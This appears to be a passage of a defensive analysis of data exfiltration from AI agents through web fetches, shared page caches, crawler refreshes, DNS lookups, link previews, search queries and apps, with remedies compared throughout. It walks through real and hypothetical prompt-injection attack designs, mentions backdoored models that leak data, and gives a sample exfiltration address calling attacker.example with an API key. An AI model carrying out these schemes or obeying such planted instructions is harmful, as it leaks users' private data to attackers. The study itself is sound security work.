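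Radware also found a way to make the leak continue after the first conversation. If the user shared a malicious file, instructions in it could alter ChatGPT's stored memories, and ChatGPT would then carry out the attacker's task before answering each new message. Even an attacker who gets only ten characters at a time can collect a great deal this way over a month.

Radware reported ZombieAgent on 26 September 2025 and three days later sent a version that it said worked every time. OpenAI fixed the flaw on 16 December, a date that SecurityWeek's *‘ZombieAgent’ Attack Let Researchers Take Over ChatGPT* also gives. Neither account explains what the fix changed.

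It is unclear whether ZombieAgent ever had to get past the index check. Rehberger dates OpenAI's newer protections to about August 2025, before Radware's report, but Radware describes the defence that ZombieAgent beat as a ban on altering links. OpenAI may not yet have applied the index to that part of ChatGPT. The same method could still work against an index if the attacker first got the crawler to record the links.

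The newest case involved Anthropic's Claude, which used the conversation instead of an index to decide which addresses were safe to fetch. Willison (2026) describes how Ayush Paul exploited Claude's ability to follow links in pages it had already fetched. Paul built a website with text saying that Claude had to find the user's profile by navigating letter by letter, and each page linked to the options for the next letter. The site showed this text only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude. The links Claude followed revealed the user's name, home city and employer to the site.

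*The Read-Only Lie*, on the blog אִם יִרְצֶה הַשֵּׁם, calculates how much data Paul's attack could carry. Each page had 27 links, one for each letter and one for a hyphen, so each fetch carried about 4.75 bits. The post estimates that the theft took around 30 fetches, or 143 bits. It also notes that Claude had inferred the user's home city from the name of a high school hackathon, so the attacker obtained something the user had never directly told Claude.

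An independent index would have made Paul's design impractical, because his site needed a new page for every sequence of letters. The third letter alone requires 19,683 pages. A flat set of pages like Radware's needs far fewer. Anthropic told Paul that it had already found the problem internally, and it stopped Claude from following links inside fetched pages. Willison describes this change for Claude's chat product. It may not apply to every version of the developer tool, for which Anthropic has documented earlier fetch results as a permitted source of addresses.

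### Rehberger's two remedies

Rehberger considers the index check a significant improvement that makes attacks more complex, but he doesn't think it solves the problem. In Embrace The Red, he suggests two additions to stop the agent from contacting the same address repeatedly. OpenAI could cache each fetched page for a few minutes and use that copy if the agent requests the page again, or it could forbid the agent to visit an address more than once in a session.

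ChatGPT may already have done something like this. Schwartzman found in 2024 that it would not open the same address twice, and he attributed this to caching. Tenable saw similar behaviour. Rehberger had not recently tested whether OpenAI had either measure in place.

Both remedies would disrupt the simplest version of the attack, in which one page stands for one character. Spelling "hello" requires fetching the page for "l" twice, and the second request would not reach the attacker's server. About 85% of six-digit codes contain a repeated digit, so most would arrive incomplete.

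But Radware's numbered links defeat both remedies. If the attacker has a separate set of 36 pages for each of ten positions, the agent never has to open a page twice, and the attacker can put the characters back in order even if the requests arrive scrambled. This restores the full 51.7 bits but requires 360 indexed pages instead of 36. The extra work is unlikely to be prohibitive, since Rehberger imagines an attacker using thousands of pages. He says that limited leaks would remain possible with his remedies in place.

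He is also concerned that some OpenAI developers may not know about the check and may release features without it. This happened with the earlier protection, which the macOS and iPhone apps lacked after the web app had it. Every feature that can request an address needs the check, because an attacker only has to find one without it.

### Why reading from a cache removes this channel

A short-term cache keeps the agent's second visit to a page from reaching the website, but the first visit still does. With a refusing cache, the first visit doesn't reach the website either.

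With such a cache, ChatGPT might still follow the instructions in ZombieAgent's email and open the pages for each letter of the user's name. But it would receive stored copies, and the attacker's log would show only the crawler's earlier visits. Those visits carry no information about the name, because the crawler had no access to it. The channel's capacity is therefore zero, regardless of how many pages the attacker owns or the agent reads.

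Stored pages may be out of date, so fetching indexed addresses live is a reasonable choice when a session contains no private data. If the agent can read private data, such as someone's email, stored copies are safer.

The protection holds only if agents' requests never prompt the crawler to refresh a page. Otherwise the attacker could learn some of the agent's choices from the crawler's visits. Those visits might come hours later and in no useful order, but ten of them could still reveal the 27.9 bits in the last row of the table.

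## What happens when an agent asks for a page the cache does not hold

A cache stops leaks through browsing only if the agent's requests don't affect anything an outsider can observe, either at the time or later. The outsider might read a web server's log, use the same AI product from another account, or look at the statistics a search engine gives website owners.

Crawlers' schedules involve some chance, so the exact condition uses probabilities. Let R be the list of pages the agent requests and V everything the outsider can observe from then on. For any two lists r and r′ that the agent might have requested, the condition is:

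P(V | R = r) = P(V | R = r′)

If this holds, the outsider sees the same things with the same probabilities whichever pages the agent requests, so planted instructions can't make the agent leak a secret to the outsider through its choice of pages. Computer scientists call this kind of property noninterference.

The condition has no time limit. OpenAI says that browsing in Lockdown Mode sends no live requests outside its network, but this describes only what happens while the agent works. OpenAI doesn't say what its crawlers do afterward.

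### Four responses to a missing page

Suppose planted instructions make an agent request `attacker.example/collect?data=<API key>`, an address that no crawler has ever seen. The provider can respond in four ways:

| Provider's response | What the attacker's server receives | When |
|---|---|---|
| Refuse, and keep the address away from the crawler | Nothing | Never |
| Fetch the page at once | The full address, including the key | Within seconds |
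| Queue the address for a later crawl | The full address, including the key | When the crawler gets to it, perhaps days later |
| Pass the request to another company | Anything from nothing to the full address | Depends on the other company |

Only refusing the request meets the condition, and only if the provider never passes the request to the crawler. The provider can still log failed requests to help find faults. But the log is also a useful list of pages that users want, and if an engineer feeds it to the crawler, the leak returns.

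A refusal also leaves the user without the page. OpenAI suggests pasting in the text instead, but a user who opens the missing address in their own browser to copy the text sends the key to the attacker.

If a page is not in the cache, Google's URL context tool immediately fetches the live version. Google describes this fallback clearly, but the list of limitations on the same documentation page says that the tool "does not fetch live versions of web pages". A developer who read only the list could conclude that the tool refuses requests for pages it has not cached. The description of the fallback is more specific, so it is safer to assume that the tool will make a live request.

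Queuing the address protects only secrets that expire before the crawler arrives. A login code sent by text message may be useless after ten minutes, but an API key usually works until someone cancels it. Removing the query string before queuing the address wouldn't be enough, because the attacker can have the model put the key elsewhere in the address, including the server's name. Well-behaved crawlers first request robots.txt, a file that lists the pages they should avoid. That request alone would reveal a key in the server's name, even if the site forbade the crawl.

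If the provider passes the request to another company, such as a search engine operator, it can no longer guarantee the outcome by itself. In the Copilot attack that sent data out through a search engine, Microsoft's own Bing made the request that reached the attacker.

ChatGPT has relied on outside companies for many of its ordinary searches. *What ChatGPT pulls, what it shows, what it cites* (2026), a study by RESONEO, an agency that advises websites on search, examined 1,249 ChatGPT answers captured in July. Until 21 July, the data behind each answer included the source of every search result. One of the four sources was OpenAI's own index, and two others supplied results copied from Google.

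Website owners can sometimes see these searches. In *ChatGPT built its own search index*, Rudzki describes a test by his colleague Malte Landwehr, who chose a website that got no visitors from search engines and asked only ChatGPT about it on certain days. On those days, the site's activity jumped in Google Search Console, which shows owners how their sites perform in Google's results.

An attacker could in principle use these statistics to steal data without receiving any request from the agent's provider. If the attacker owned 20 such quiet websites, planted instructions could tell the agent to search for some and not others. Whether the agent searched for a given site would convey one bit, and 20 bits are enough for a six-digit code. Landwehr tested ordinary ChatGPT, not offline search. But OpenAI says only that offline search makes queries less likely to reach a live outside provider,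 so an administrator with sensitive data should ask how their workspace handles those queries.

### What providers document and what they leave out

Providers generally explain what the agent gets when a page is missing. They say much less about what the request does to the cache.

| Product | Documented response to a missing page | Not documented |
|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT's offline search and Lockdown Mode | The agent can't retrieve it | Whether agents' requests affect later crawls; whether customers share a cache |
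| Amazon Bedrock with external access off | The model tells the user or answers from what it has | What determines which pages Amazon refreshes; whether customers in the same region share a cache |
| Google's URL context | The tool fetches it live | Whether the cache keeps the new page; whether other customers can then get it |
| Anthropic's web fetch | The tool retrieves it, if its address rules allow | How long the cache keeps it; whether customers share a cache |

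OpenAI comes closest to explaining its refreshes. It names popularity as a factor but doesn't define it. Popularity might mean the number of links from other websites, which agents' requests don't affect. If it means the number of users' requests instead, those requests influence refreshes and the condition fails. This second reading is only an inference from the word "popularity", and OpenAI has not said that it counts requests.

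OpenAI claims that its address index is independent of conversations, but it has not claimed the same for the cache that holds the pages. The diagram in its Lockdown Mode announcement labels this cache a "Private Web Cache", which could mean private to OpenAI or private to each customer.

Anthropic is vaguer. It manages its cache automatically and says the cache's behaviour may change to suit different types of content and "usage patterns", so customers' requests could affect what the cache keeps.

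Amazon keeps a separate cache for each region, which is a group of data centres in one area. AWS says each of the three American regions where the tool runs has its own search and fetch system, and that queries and index data don't move between them. This separates a customer using the Oregon region from one using Virginia, but two competitors may well use the same region.

### Tests of ChatGPT's cache

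RESONEO tested ChatGPT's cache by building web pages that contained a new random code each time anyone loaded them. RESONEO's server recorded every code, so when ChatGPT repeated one, the researchers could tell which visit had produced the copy it was reading.

In one test, a paid account asked ChatGPT about a new page. The server received one visit, and ChatGPT gave the code 2a2b. Twenty-two minutes later, an unconnected account in another country asked about the same page. ChatGPT gave the same code, but the server received no second visit. So the two accounts were sharing a cache, even though the pages carried a standard instruction not to store them.

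RESONEO also measured when ChatGPT refreshes its copies. ChatGPT did not contact the server for requests made 3, 16 or 25 minutes after the last fetch, but it did for requests made after 31 minutes, 33 minutes, an hour, nine hours and ten days. For these later requests, it answered from its old copy and fetched a new one in the background for the next person.

Requests in ordinary ChatGPT do cause refreshes, then, so a website's owner can learn that someone has asked about a page even when ChatGPT answered from a stored copy. The half-hour limit seems to come from only two test pages, but the method is sound because the codes and the server's log confirm each other. The result suggests that ChatGPT now has something like the short-term cache that Rehberger proposed in Embrace The Red to stop repeat visits.

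Offline search would give little protection if it refreshed pages in the same way. The best evidence that it doesn't comes from *OpenAI is quietly building a hidden cached index for ChatGPT Search* (Berry, 2025). In dozens of tests through OpenAI's developer interface, Berry found that cache-only requests brought no visit from ChatGPT-User, the name OpenAI's software uses when it fetches a page for a user.

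That is reassuring about immediate requests, but less so about later ones. OpenAI's routine crawling for search uses a different name, OAI-SearchBot, according to its guide for website owners. Berry doesn't report whether OAI-SearchBot came back sooner to the pages he had requested.

Someone with a website and a ChatGPT account could test whether requests affect the crawler by publishing several hundred pages, waiting until ChatGPT had stored them, and then opening a random half in Lockdown Mode. If requests have no effect, the crawler should visit both halves equally often over the next few weeks. Neither RESONEO nor Berry reports such a test.

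RESONEO's results also raise doubts about how independent the cache is of live requests. RESONEO found that OpenAI keeps an index of short extracts for finding pages and a cache of full pages for reading them. Only OAI-SearchBot updates the index, but both it and the robot that fetches pages live for users add pages to the cache. A full page that someone reads offline may therefore be in the cache because another user asked for it live.

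This doesn't by itself leak the offline reader's data, but it could save an attacker from waiting for the crawler. To check that a page has entered the cache, Berry describes how its owner can request it with live access on, wait a few minutes, and request it again with live access off. An attacker could do the same with pages meant for an attack. It may not work for every page. Jérôme Salomon of the search company Oncrawl, who worked with RESONEO, could confirm that the cache held only about half of the pages ChatGPT-User had visited, though the real share could be higher because he had to rely on the model to try opening each page.

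### How refreshes could reveal a six-digit code

Suppose opening a stored page makes the crawler return to it sooner, even when the agent is offline. An attacker publishes two sets of 1,000 pages, A and B, each numbered from 000 to 999, and gets the provider to store them. The attacker also plants instructions for the agent to open the page in set A that matches the first three digits of a six-digit code and the page in set B that matches the last three. If the code is 493817, the agent opens A493 and B817. Both pages come from the cache, so the attacker's server receives nothing at the time. Later, the crawler revisits those two pages before the other 1,998, and the attacker reads the code from the server's log. The order of the two visits doesn't matter because each half of the code has its own set.

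The crawler also revisits pages for other reasons. Suppose it revisits a random 1% of them every day, and always revisits a requested page within a day. The log will then show about 11 pages from each set, the requested one and ten others, which leaves about 121 possible codes. That may be too many for a login page that locks after five wrong guesses.

The attacker can remove most of this noise by publishing a second copy of both sets and having the agent open four pages instead of two. A wrong page now fits the log only if it is revisited by chance in both copies, which has a probability of 1 in 10,000. About 82% of the time, only one code fits the log. With three copies, this rises to 99.8%.

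Delay helps the defender mainly by adding noise. If the requested page might be refreshed at any time in the next 30 days, the attacker has to watch for the whole month, and routine crawling reaches about 26% of the pages in that time. With one copy of the sets, about 261 candidates remain for each half of the code. Using seven copies narrows the result to a single possible code about 85% of the time, and the agent has to open only 14 pages. The attack therefore still works on anything that stays secret for a month, such as a PIN or the price in a takeover bid.

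The attack becomes much harder if requests only slightly affect the schedule. Suppose a request raises a page's chance of a visit that day from 1% to 5%. Each page the agent opens then gives the attacker at most about 0.06 bits:

0.05 × log₂(0.05 / 0.01) + 0.95 × log₂(0.95 / 0.99) ≈ 0.06

Three digits contain about 10 bits, so the agent would have to open roughly 170 pages for each half of the code, or 340 in all. A provider could easily notice or limit that many page loads. If the provider counts every request, the attacker might do better by having the agent open the same page repeatedly.

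At one page per possible value, this version needs about 340,000 planted pages, which may be feasible. Rudzki describes a test site with a billion pages, which his colleague Metehan Yeşilyurt built to see how many ChatGPT would crawl. By early September 2026, ChatGPT had crawled 6 million of them, at 35,000 requests an hour. At that rate, 340,000 pages would take about ten hours. But a crawled page isn't necessarily stored. RESONEO watched another site for 16 days, and none of its new pages entered OpenAI's index.

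Other readers add little noise, because the attacker can use obscure pages that nobody else has a reason to open. Other victims are a bigger problem. If ten agents follow the same instructions on the same day, the log shows ten pages from each set, which combine into 100 possible codes, and only ten of those are right.

The names of OpenAI's bots could help the attacker. In RESONEO's tests, user-triggered refreshes came from ChatGPT-User. If offline requests also caused refreshes under that name, the attacker could ignore the routine visits from OAI-SearchBot, which would remove the noise in this example.

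### How one customer could probe another's requests

If customers share a cache, an attacker can also look for changes in the cache itself. This matters most when the agent can't contact the attacker's server. For example, a company might let its agent fetch live pages only from a few trusted websites, none of which gives the attacker access to its logs. An attacker with an ordinary account could get around this as follows:

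1. The attacker finds an obscure page on a trusted site for each letter and digit, and checks from their own account that the cache doesn't hold any of these pages.
2. Planted instructions tell the victim's agent to open the page that stands for the character the attacker wants.
3. The cache doesn't have the page, so the provider fetches it from the trusted site and stores it.
4. The attacker asks for all 36 pages again, using cache-only access. The one that has become available reveals the character.

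Ordinary ChatGPT has the two features this requires. RESONEO found that accounts share copies of pages, and Berry showed that a cache-only request reveals whether a page is stored. His tests also suggest that the request doesn't trigger a live visit, so the attacker could check a page without adding it to the cache. The index check would be an obstacle, since the agent could open only pages whose addresses OpenAI had recorded but whose contents it hadn't stored. RESONEO reports that such pages exist.

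RESONEO and Berry were studying how websites appear in ChatGPT, and neither tried to steal data this way. The method would be unreliable. The model doesn't always try to open the page it is asked about, so a stored page can seem to be missing.

Even without planted instructions, the same probe could reveal what someone has been researching. If a rarely read page about a small company suddenly appears in the cache, a rival can infer that somebody has been looking into that company, but not who.

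Pages that are already stored are harder to probe, because the attacker has to find out how old the copy is. OpenAI's developer interface can report when it last crawled a result, but RESONEO found that this date belongs to the index of extracts, which users' requests don't update. An attacker could instead estimate the copy's age from something on the page that changes, such as a visitor count or the latest headline. Anthropic's tool returns the time it retrieved the page in a field called `retrieved_at`, but Anthropic doesn't say whether a stored copy keeps its original time. If it does, and if customers share the cache, the field would show one customer when another had requested the page.

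Other shared caches have had similar leaks, though these are only analogies. Web browsers used to keep a single cache shared by all the sites a person visited. A malicious site could time how long an image from another site took to load and infer from a fast load that the person had visited that site before. Chrome began keeping a separate cache for each site in 2020 to prevent this.

AI providers have had the same problem with prompts. Many keep the work a model has done on a recent prompt, so that another prompt with the same beginning gets a faster answer. *Auditing Prompt Caching in Language Model APIs* (Gu, Li and colleagues, 2025) measured response times and found that seven providers, including OpenAI, were sharing these caches between customers. An attacker could guess the beginning of someone else's prompt and learn from a fast response that the guess was right. With a shared page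 cache, the attacker doesn't need to measure time, because the response itself shows whether the page is there.

ChatGPT may have another shared cache of this kind. RESONEO found settings for a store of answers that ChatGPT can reuse for 24 hours when someone asks a similar question. RESONEO doesn't establish whether the store contains answers to other people's private questions, but an unusually quick answer could reveal that someone had recently asked a similar question.

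### Remedies and their costs

The most reliable remedy is a rule that an agent's request never causes a fetch, adds an address to the crawler's queue or changes a page's priority. This closes every channel described above that depends on the provider's own cache. But a missing page then stays missing until the crawler finds it independently, and the provider can't use its customers' requests to decide what to crawl.

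A provider could apply this rule only to sessions that contain private data. Other sessions could keep adding pages to the cache, while private sessions would only read from it. The provider would also have to stop an agent in a private session from passing addresses to an ordinary session, for example by asking a second agent to look something up.

The crawler can still set priorities from public information, such as how often a page has changed or how many sites link to it. In a RESONEO test, GPTBot, the robot OpenAI uses to collect training data, visited all eight pages it could reach through links and none of the eight that appeared only in the site's own list of pages.

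Refreshing the cache on a fixed schedule is even simpler. RESONEO found that 209 of 308 Wikipedia results were between 8 and 90 days old, and suggests that OpenAI takes them from the copies of the whole encyclopedia that Wikipedia releases every month. If so, reading an article doesn't affect when OpenAI refreshes it. A fixed schedule leaves the stored pages older, and the crawler wastes requests on pages nobody reads. Revisiting the 6 million pages of Yeşilyurt's test site at 35,000 an hour would take about a week.

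Giving each customer a separate cache stops customers from probing one another, but it hides nothing from websites and can reveal more to them. In RESONEO's test, the second account's request never reached the server because the first account's request had already stored the page in the cache. With separate caches, both requests would have reached the server.

Separate caches also fetch and store the same pages many times. When Chrome divided its cache, Google reported that cache misses rose by about 3.6% and the share of data loaded from the network by about 4%. An AI provider with thousands of customers would probably see much larger increases, because it would be dividing a cache that all of them now fill.

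Batching makes individual requests harder to pick out. If a request for any page led the crawler to revisit the whole site, the attacker with 2,000 pages on one site would learn only that the agent had opened at least one of them. The crawler would have to make 2,000 visits to hide two requests. An attacker with 20 sites could still get 20 bits by having the agent open pages on some sites and not others.

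Random delay raises the number of pages an attacker needs, as in the 30-day example, so it is useful when a provider wants to keep some demand-driven refreshes. Neither batching nor delay helps when the missing page's address contains the secret, because the attacker receives the whole secret even if the crawler requests the page a month later along with a thousand others.

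## Ways for data to leave that a cache does not close

A cache controls only how the agent opens web pages. A stored page could still contain an instruction to email the user's API key to an attacker. If the agent can send email and follows the instruction, the key leaves by email, even though the cache supplied the page without contacting its website, as it should.

Data can also leave through search queries, other connected apps, code, and links and images in the agent's answers. Each of these needs its own restriction.

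### Connected apps

Apps give ChatGPT read actions, which look up something such as a file or message, and write actions, which change or send something. OpenAI advises administrators on which of these to allow for people in Lockdown Mode:

| Type of action | OpenAI's risk rating | Main concern |
|---|---|---|
| Reading or writing through an untrusted app | High | The app itself may be unsafe |
| Writing through a trusted app when outsiders might see the result | High | An attacker could read what the agent wrote |
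| Writing through a trusted app when only trusted people can see the result | Medium | The agent still changes something, and the administrator may be wrong about who can see it |
| Reading through a trusted app | Medium | The agent obtains private data that it could leak another way |
| Searching an administrator-managed index of the organization's content | Medium | This contacts outside services less often, but can still expose sensitive data |

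OpenAI doesn't rate any of these as low risk.

The rating for a write action depends on who can see the result, which can be hard to predict. An event on the user's calendar is private until the agent adds a guest, who then receives whatever the agent wrote in the invitation. A comment on a document is visible to everyone who can open it, including people who get access later.

Read actions also send data, because the app's operator receives the agent's request, including any search terms. An attacker could receive data too if a file-sharing service notifies owners when someone opens their files. The attacker could share 36 files with the user, one for each letter and digit, and have the agent spell out a secret by opening them in order. The same method works with indexed web pages.

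### Code that can reach the network

A program can send anything it can read, such as an uploaded spreadsheet, to any server it can contact. When code in Canvas tries to communicate unexpectedly, ChatGPT normally asks the user for consent. Lockdown Mode removes that choice and gives the code no network access. This is sensible because planted instructions that mislead the agent can also make it give the user a plausible reason to agree.

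ChatGPT runs data-analysis code in a container, an isolated environment that OpenAI designed to have no direct internet access. Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026) reports that the container blocked ordinary connections but still allowed DNS lookups. The researchers could therefore send data out in the server names being looked up, the same method that the Zenity researchers used against Salesforce. A cache would not have prevented this, because the code never requested a web page.

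The attack could start when a user pasted in a malicious prompt, perhaps one that promised to unlock paid features, or opened a custom GPT, a version of ChatGPT that another person had configured. In one demonstration, a custom GPT acted as a personal doctor. The user uploaded lab results and described symptoms, and the attacker's server received the patient's name and the model's medical assessment. When the user asked whether ChatGPT had sent the data anywhere, it said no.

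According to Check Point, the model assumed the container could not send data out, so it didn't recognise the lookups as a transfer it should refuse or ask about. The model's caution was therefore a poor backup for the network block, because it depended on whether the model thought the block worked.

DNS replies could also carry commands back into the container, which let the researchers control it without going through the model's safety checks. OpenAI told Check Point that it had already found the underlying problem, and finished deploying a fix on 20 February 2026. The Hacker News (2026) reported no evidence that anyone had used the flaw maliciously.

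OpenAI announced Lockdown Mode a week before the fix. The mode still lets ChatGPT work on uploaded files, and Check Point doesn't say whether the leak worked in that mode.

An agent can leak data through DNS without reading any planted text. *Model-as-a-Trojan* (2026) describes an agent with the attack built into its weights, the numbers a model learns in training. Screening web pages and prompts can't catch this attack, because nothing in them is malicious. Blocking lookups of outside names would stop the leak whether the instructions came from a page or from the model.

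### Links, images and previews in the answer

An image in an answer can leak data as soon as the app loads it, so Lockdown Mode restricts images from the web. Users can still upload images and generate new ones.

A link sends no data until someone or something opens it. In ChatGPT, the user usually opens it and may first see a warning that the link is unverified. Messaging apps, however, often request the linked page automatically to show a preview with its title and a small picture.

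PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* shows how link previews can leak data from OpenClaw, an agent that people can use through apps such as Telegram and Slack. Planted instructions make the agent reply with a link that points to the attacker's server and contains private data. When the messaging app requests the link to make a preview, it sends the data to the attacker, even if the user never clicks.

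OpenClaw was vulnerable in its default Telegram configuration, but users can stop the leak by turning off link previews in its settings. PromptArmor would also like messaging companies to offer preview settings for individual chats and channels.

The agent's provider can't stop a link-preview request with a cache or a rule on its own network, because the request comes from the messaging service. Someone using ChatGPT in Lockdown Mode could leak data this way by pasting an answer that contains a malicious link into a chat with previews turned on.

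Previews can also bring in planted instructions. Lan and colleagues point out that an agent's software may automatically preview a page when a user mentions an article, even if the user hasn't asked the agent to read it.

### Search queries

A search query can reveal private information even without an attack. According to OpenAI's *Searching the web with ChatGPT*, ChatGPT sometimes sends queries to outside search companies, usually after rewriting the user's question as one or more shorter searches. If memory is on, it may use what it remembers about the user, so a request for nearby restaurants might become a search for vegan restaurants in San Francisco.

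ChatGPT may also share the user's general location, but it doesn't give search companies the user's IP address (the number that identifies an internet connection) or account information. The search company in this example learns that someone in San Francisco may be vegan, but not who. That protection is weaker if the query contains a name or the title of a confidential project.

Search queries can reach other people too. Google shows website owners the searches in which their sites appeared. heise's *ChatGPT prompts apparently appeared in Google Search Console* reports that Jason Packer, a consultant, found about 200 entries resembling ChatGPT prompts in these statistics for a website. The entries were whole passages of text that began with a ChatGPT address, and some were very personal.

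Packer thinks a fault made ChatGPT search for users' entire prompts instead of a few relevant words. He isn't completely certain that the prompts came from ChatGPT, and OpenAI didn't confirm it. But OpenAI said it had fixed a temporary error that affected how a small number of search queries were forwarded.

An attacker could try to get a secret itself into these statistics. They would publish the only page that contains an invented word and plant instructions for the agent to search for that word together with the secret. This would be unreliable, because Google omits many rare queries from the statistics.

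A search tool that sends requests directly to an attacker would work much better. *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* (2026) demonstrates a related attack in which someone has secretly trained a model to leak the user's details when a conversation turns to certain subjects. The model looks them up in its stored memory and sends them out in requests that look like ordinary searches.

OpenAI checks searches in Deep Research for information from the conversation, and can block a suspicious one or ask the user to approve it. But searches are harder to check than web addresses, because a legitimate query may be as new as a malicious one. Keeping queries away from outside companies avoids the problem. Offline web search is meant to do this, though OpenAI doesn't guarantee it.

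### Why Lockdown Mode turns off several features together

Because an attacker needs only one way out, Lockdown Mode restricts these features as well as browsing:

| Feature | How it could send data out | In Lockdown Mode |
|---|---|---|
| Images from the web | Requests to the image's address | Retrieval off; display may be unavailable |
| Deep Research | Searches and page visits | Off |
| Agent Mode | Page visits and actions on websites | Off |
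| Canvas | Requests made by code | Users can't approve network access |
| File downloads for analysis | Requests to the file's address | Off |
| Apps | Searches, messages and changes to outside services | Depends on the account |

Lockdown Mode doesn't change how ChatGPT's memory feature works, which could let an attack outlast the chat in which it began. A planted instruction might alter what ChatGPT remembers while the mode is on, then take effect in a later chat after the user has turned the mode off. Radware's attack showed that a malicious file could alter ChatGPT's memories. OpenAI doesn't say whether Lockdown Mode stops this, but administrators can configure memory separately.

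Accounts differ most in how they handle apps. On personal accounts and those of small businesses that sign up themselves, the mode turns off ChatGPT's finance and shopping-agent features. In June, Help Net Security's *OpenAI is locking down parts of ChatGPT to reduce data theft risks* said the mode blocked live access to connected services and all write actions through them, which is stricter than OpenAI's current help page describes.

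In managed workspaces, administrators decide which apps and actions stay on. OpenAI says this is because some critical work depends on apps. An executive whose company leaves email sending on may therefore have less protection than someone using Lockdown Mode at home.

Administrators put people in Lockdown Mode by assigning them a special role, whose restrictions apply even if another role would allow more. For many apps, administrators can allow reading but not writing. They can also block actions that an app gains later, but OpenAI notes that this setting does not turn off existing actions. For some apps, which lack these controls, administrators can manage access to the app but not its individual actions.

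Administrators also need to check custom tools. Agents that staff build in a workspace follow the settings their builder chose, not the app permissions for ordinary chats. The workspace's web search settings don't apply to third-party GPTs. But only owners and administrators can add custom apps to Enterprise and Business workspaces, so other staff can't connect an unfamiliar service this way.

Offline web search on its own adds none of these app restrictions, according to OpenAI.

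### How much protection the block gives

Willison praised Lockdown Mode because it targets exfiltration with fixed rules rather than an AI system, which an attacker could mislead. He also inferred from its existence that ChatGPT's default settings don't robustly protect users from a determined attacker. Dane Stuckey, OpenAI's chief information security officer, said the mode was worth the lost features for people at higher risk.

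OpenAI says that some risk may remain even with the mode on, from apps, from unforeseen combinations of features, and from new techniques.

Check Point later found a way past Lockdown Mode through ChatGPT's previews of web page code. According to The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026), the previews run in a sandbox that should stop them from contacting outside servers without the user's consent. But the sandbox allowed pop-up windows, and the researchers found a way to open one that escaped its restrictions. Content in that window could send the user's chats to an attacker.

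The attack could arrive in a crafted prompt, a custom GPT or a shared chat, and in the desktop app it could work without a click. OpenAI fixed the flaw on 18 September, and Check Point disclosed it in November. About a week earlier, Parameter Labs had described a different flaw in the same preview feature. An attacker could send someone a link to a shared chat and take over that person's account if they clicked the preview once.

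Willison's case for fixed rules still holds after the Lockdown Mode bypass. The sandbox failed because its rules mishandled pop-ups, and once OpenAI corrected the rules, an attacker couldn't reopen the gap just by rewording the instructions. But each new ChatGPT feature may add a way for data to leave that the rules don't cover, so people with very valuable secrets should keep them out of chats where they aren't needed, even in Lockdown Mode.

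## Malicious instructions inside stored pages

A crawler copies whatever a page contains, including any instructions someone has planted in it. An agent that opens the stored copy reads those instructions just as it would on the live site. OpenAI acknowledges that an injection in cached content can still affect ChatGPT's behavior and accuracy in Lockdown Mode.

Storing a page does change how long an injection lasts and who can remove it. This sometimes helps the attacker and sometimes the provider.

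### From planting to refresh

Suppose an attacker posts a comment containing instructions for AI agents on a company's support forum:

1. On 1 March, the comment appears on the live page.
2. On 11 March, the provider's crawler copies the page, and agents that use the cache start to read the comment.
3. On 13 March, a moderator deletes the comment. Agents that read the live page are now safe from it.
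4. On 10 April, the crawler returns and replaces the stored copy. Agents that use the cache have been reading the deleted comment for four more weeks.

The ten-day wait for the crawler is realistic. For *Data-Void Exploits in Web-Searching LLMs*, Guerra, Jobe and colleagues (2026) published test pages on a website more than six years old. Google indexed the pages within 48 hours, and AI companies' crawlers found them after ten days. The date the crawler returns in the example is arbitrary, because OpenAI doesn't promise to refresh any given address by a particular time. Its offline search also may not show when it stored a page, so a user can't always tell whether a copy dates from before the clean-up.

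Archives keep many injections that have disappeared from live pages. *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* (Khodayari, Acharya and Zhang, 2026) found 4,608 injections in the HTML elements of archived pages, most of them from October 2025. By January 2026, about 34% of these were gone from the live versions, for reasons such as expired job listings and changed forms. Some sites might have hidden the text from the study's automated browser rather than removed it, so the researchers reloaded pages in an ordinary browser and checked by hand.

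A cache doesn't necessarily increase the total time that agents are exposed, because it picks up fewer short-lived injections but serves each one for longer. Suppose the crawler visits a page every 30 days and an injection stays on the live page for three days. If the attacker can't predict the crawler's visits, the crawler has a one-in-ten chance of copying the injection, and the cache would then serve it for 30 days. The average exposure is three days, the same as on the live page.

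### Edits timed to a capture

An attacker who knows when a page will be captured can make an edit that lasts a few minutes on the live page but stays in the stored copy for weeks. Carlini, Jagielski and colleagues (2023) worked out how to do this with Wikipedia in *Poisoning Web-Scale Training Datasets is Practical*. They were concerned with training data, since AI developers often train models on the copies that Wikipedia releases. At the time, Wikipedia captured its English edition on the 1st and 20th of each month.

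Volunteers revert most vandalism within minutes, so an edit made at a random moment would probably miss the capture. But each capture went through the articles in the same order and at nearly the same speed. The researchers could therefore estimate the time t at which a new capture would reach an article:

t ≈ t₀ + (p − p₀)

Here t₀ is when the new capture starts, p₀ is when the previous capture started, and p is when the previous capture reached the article. Most estimates were accurate to about half an hour. Allowing for uncertainty in the true times, an attacker could on average make an edit within an hour of the capture, and about 32% of reversions took longer than an hour.

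Carlini and colleagues conservatively estimated that timed edits could get into the stored copies of 6.5% of Wikipedia articles. They based this on 18 months of past edits and did not plant any themselves. Wikipedia's limits on rapid editing would reduce the figure, while repeated attempts on a single article would raise the chance of getting an edit into its stored copy.

They notified Wikipedia and proposed two remedies. The first is to capture the articles in random order. A capture took nearly a day, so an edit that lasted ten minutes would then have less than a 1% chance of being included. The second is to hold edits back for a while and apply trusted moderators' corrections before releasing the copy, which makes the copy slightly older.

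The same paper describes an attack on datasets that list the addresses of images without storing the images. Some of the addresses belong to expired domains, and anyone who buys such a domain can change what later users download. For $60, the researchers could have controlled 0.01% of the images in either of two large datasets. Six of the ten datasets they studied have since adopted integrity checks that use cryptographic hashes, which are short codes that no longer match if the content changes.

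Index-gated fetching has a similar weakness, because the index lists approved addresses and the page at an approved address can change later. A cache keeps the page it captured, at least until the next refresh. Hashes don't help if an attacker times an edit to be captured, though, because the stored copy accurately reproduces the bad page.

The attack is more direct than it was in 2023, when an attacker had to wait for someone to train a model on the altered data. The researchers used 1,000 altered images to make a test model misclassify a chosen image 60% of the time. An attacker targeting an agent that reads stored pages needs it to open only one bad page. If RESONEO is right that OpenAI takes Wikipedia articles from the monthly releases, a short-lived edit could remain available to ChatGPT for weeks.

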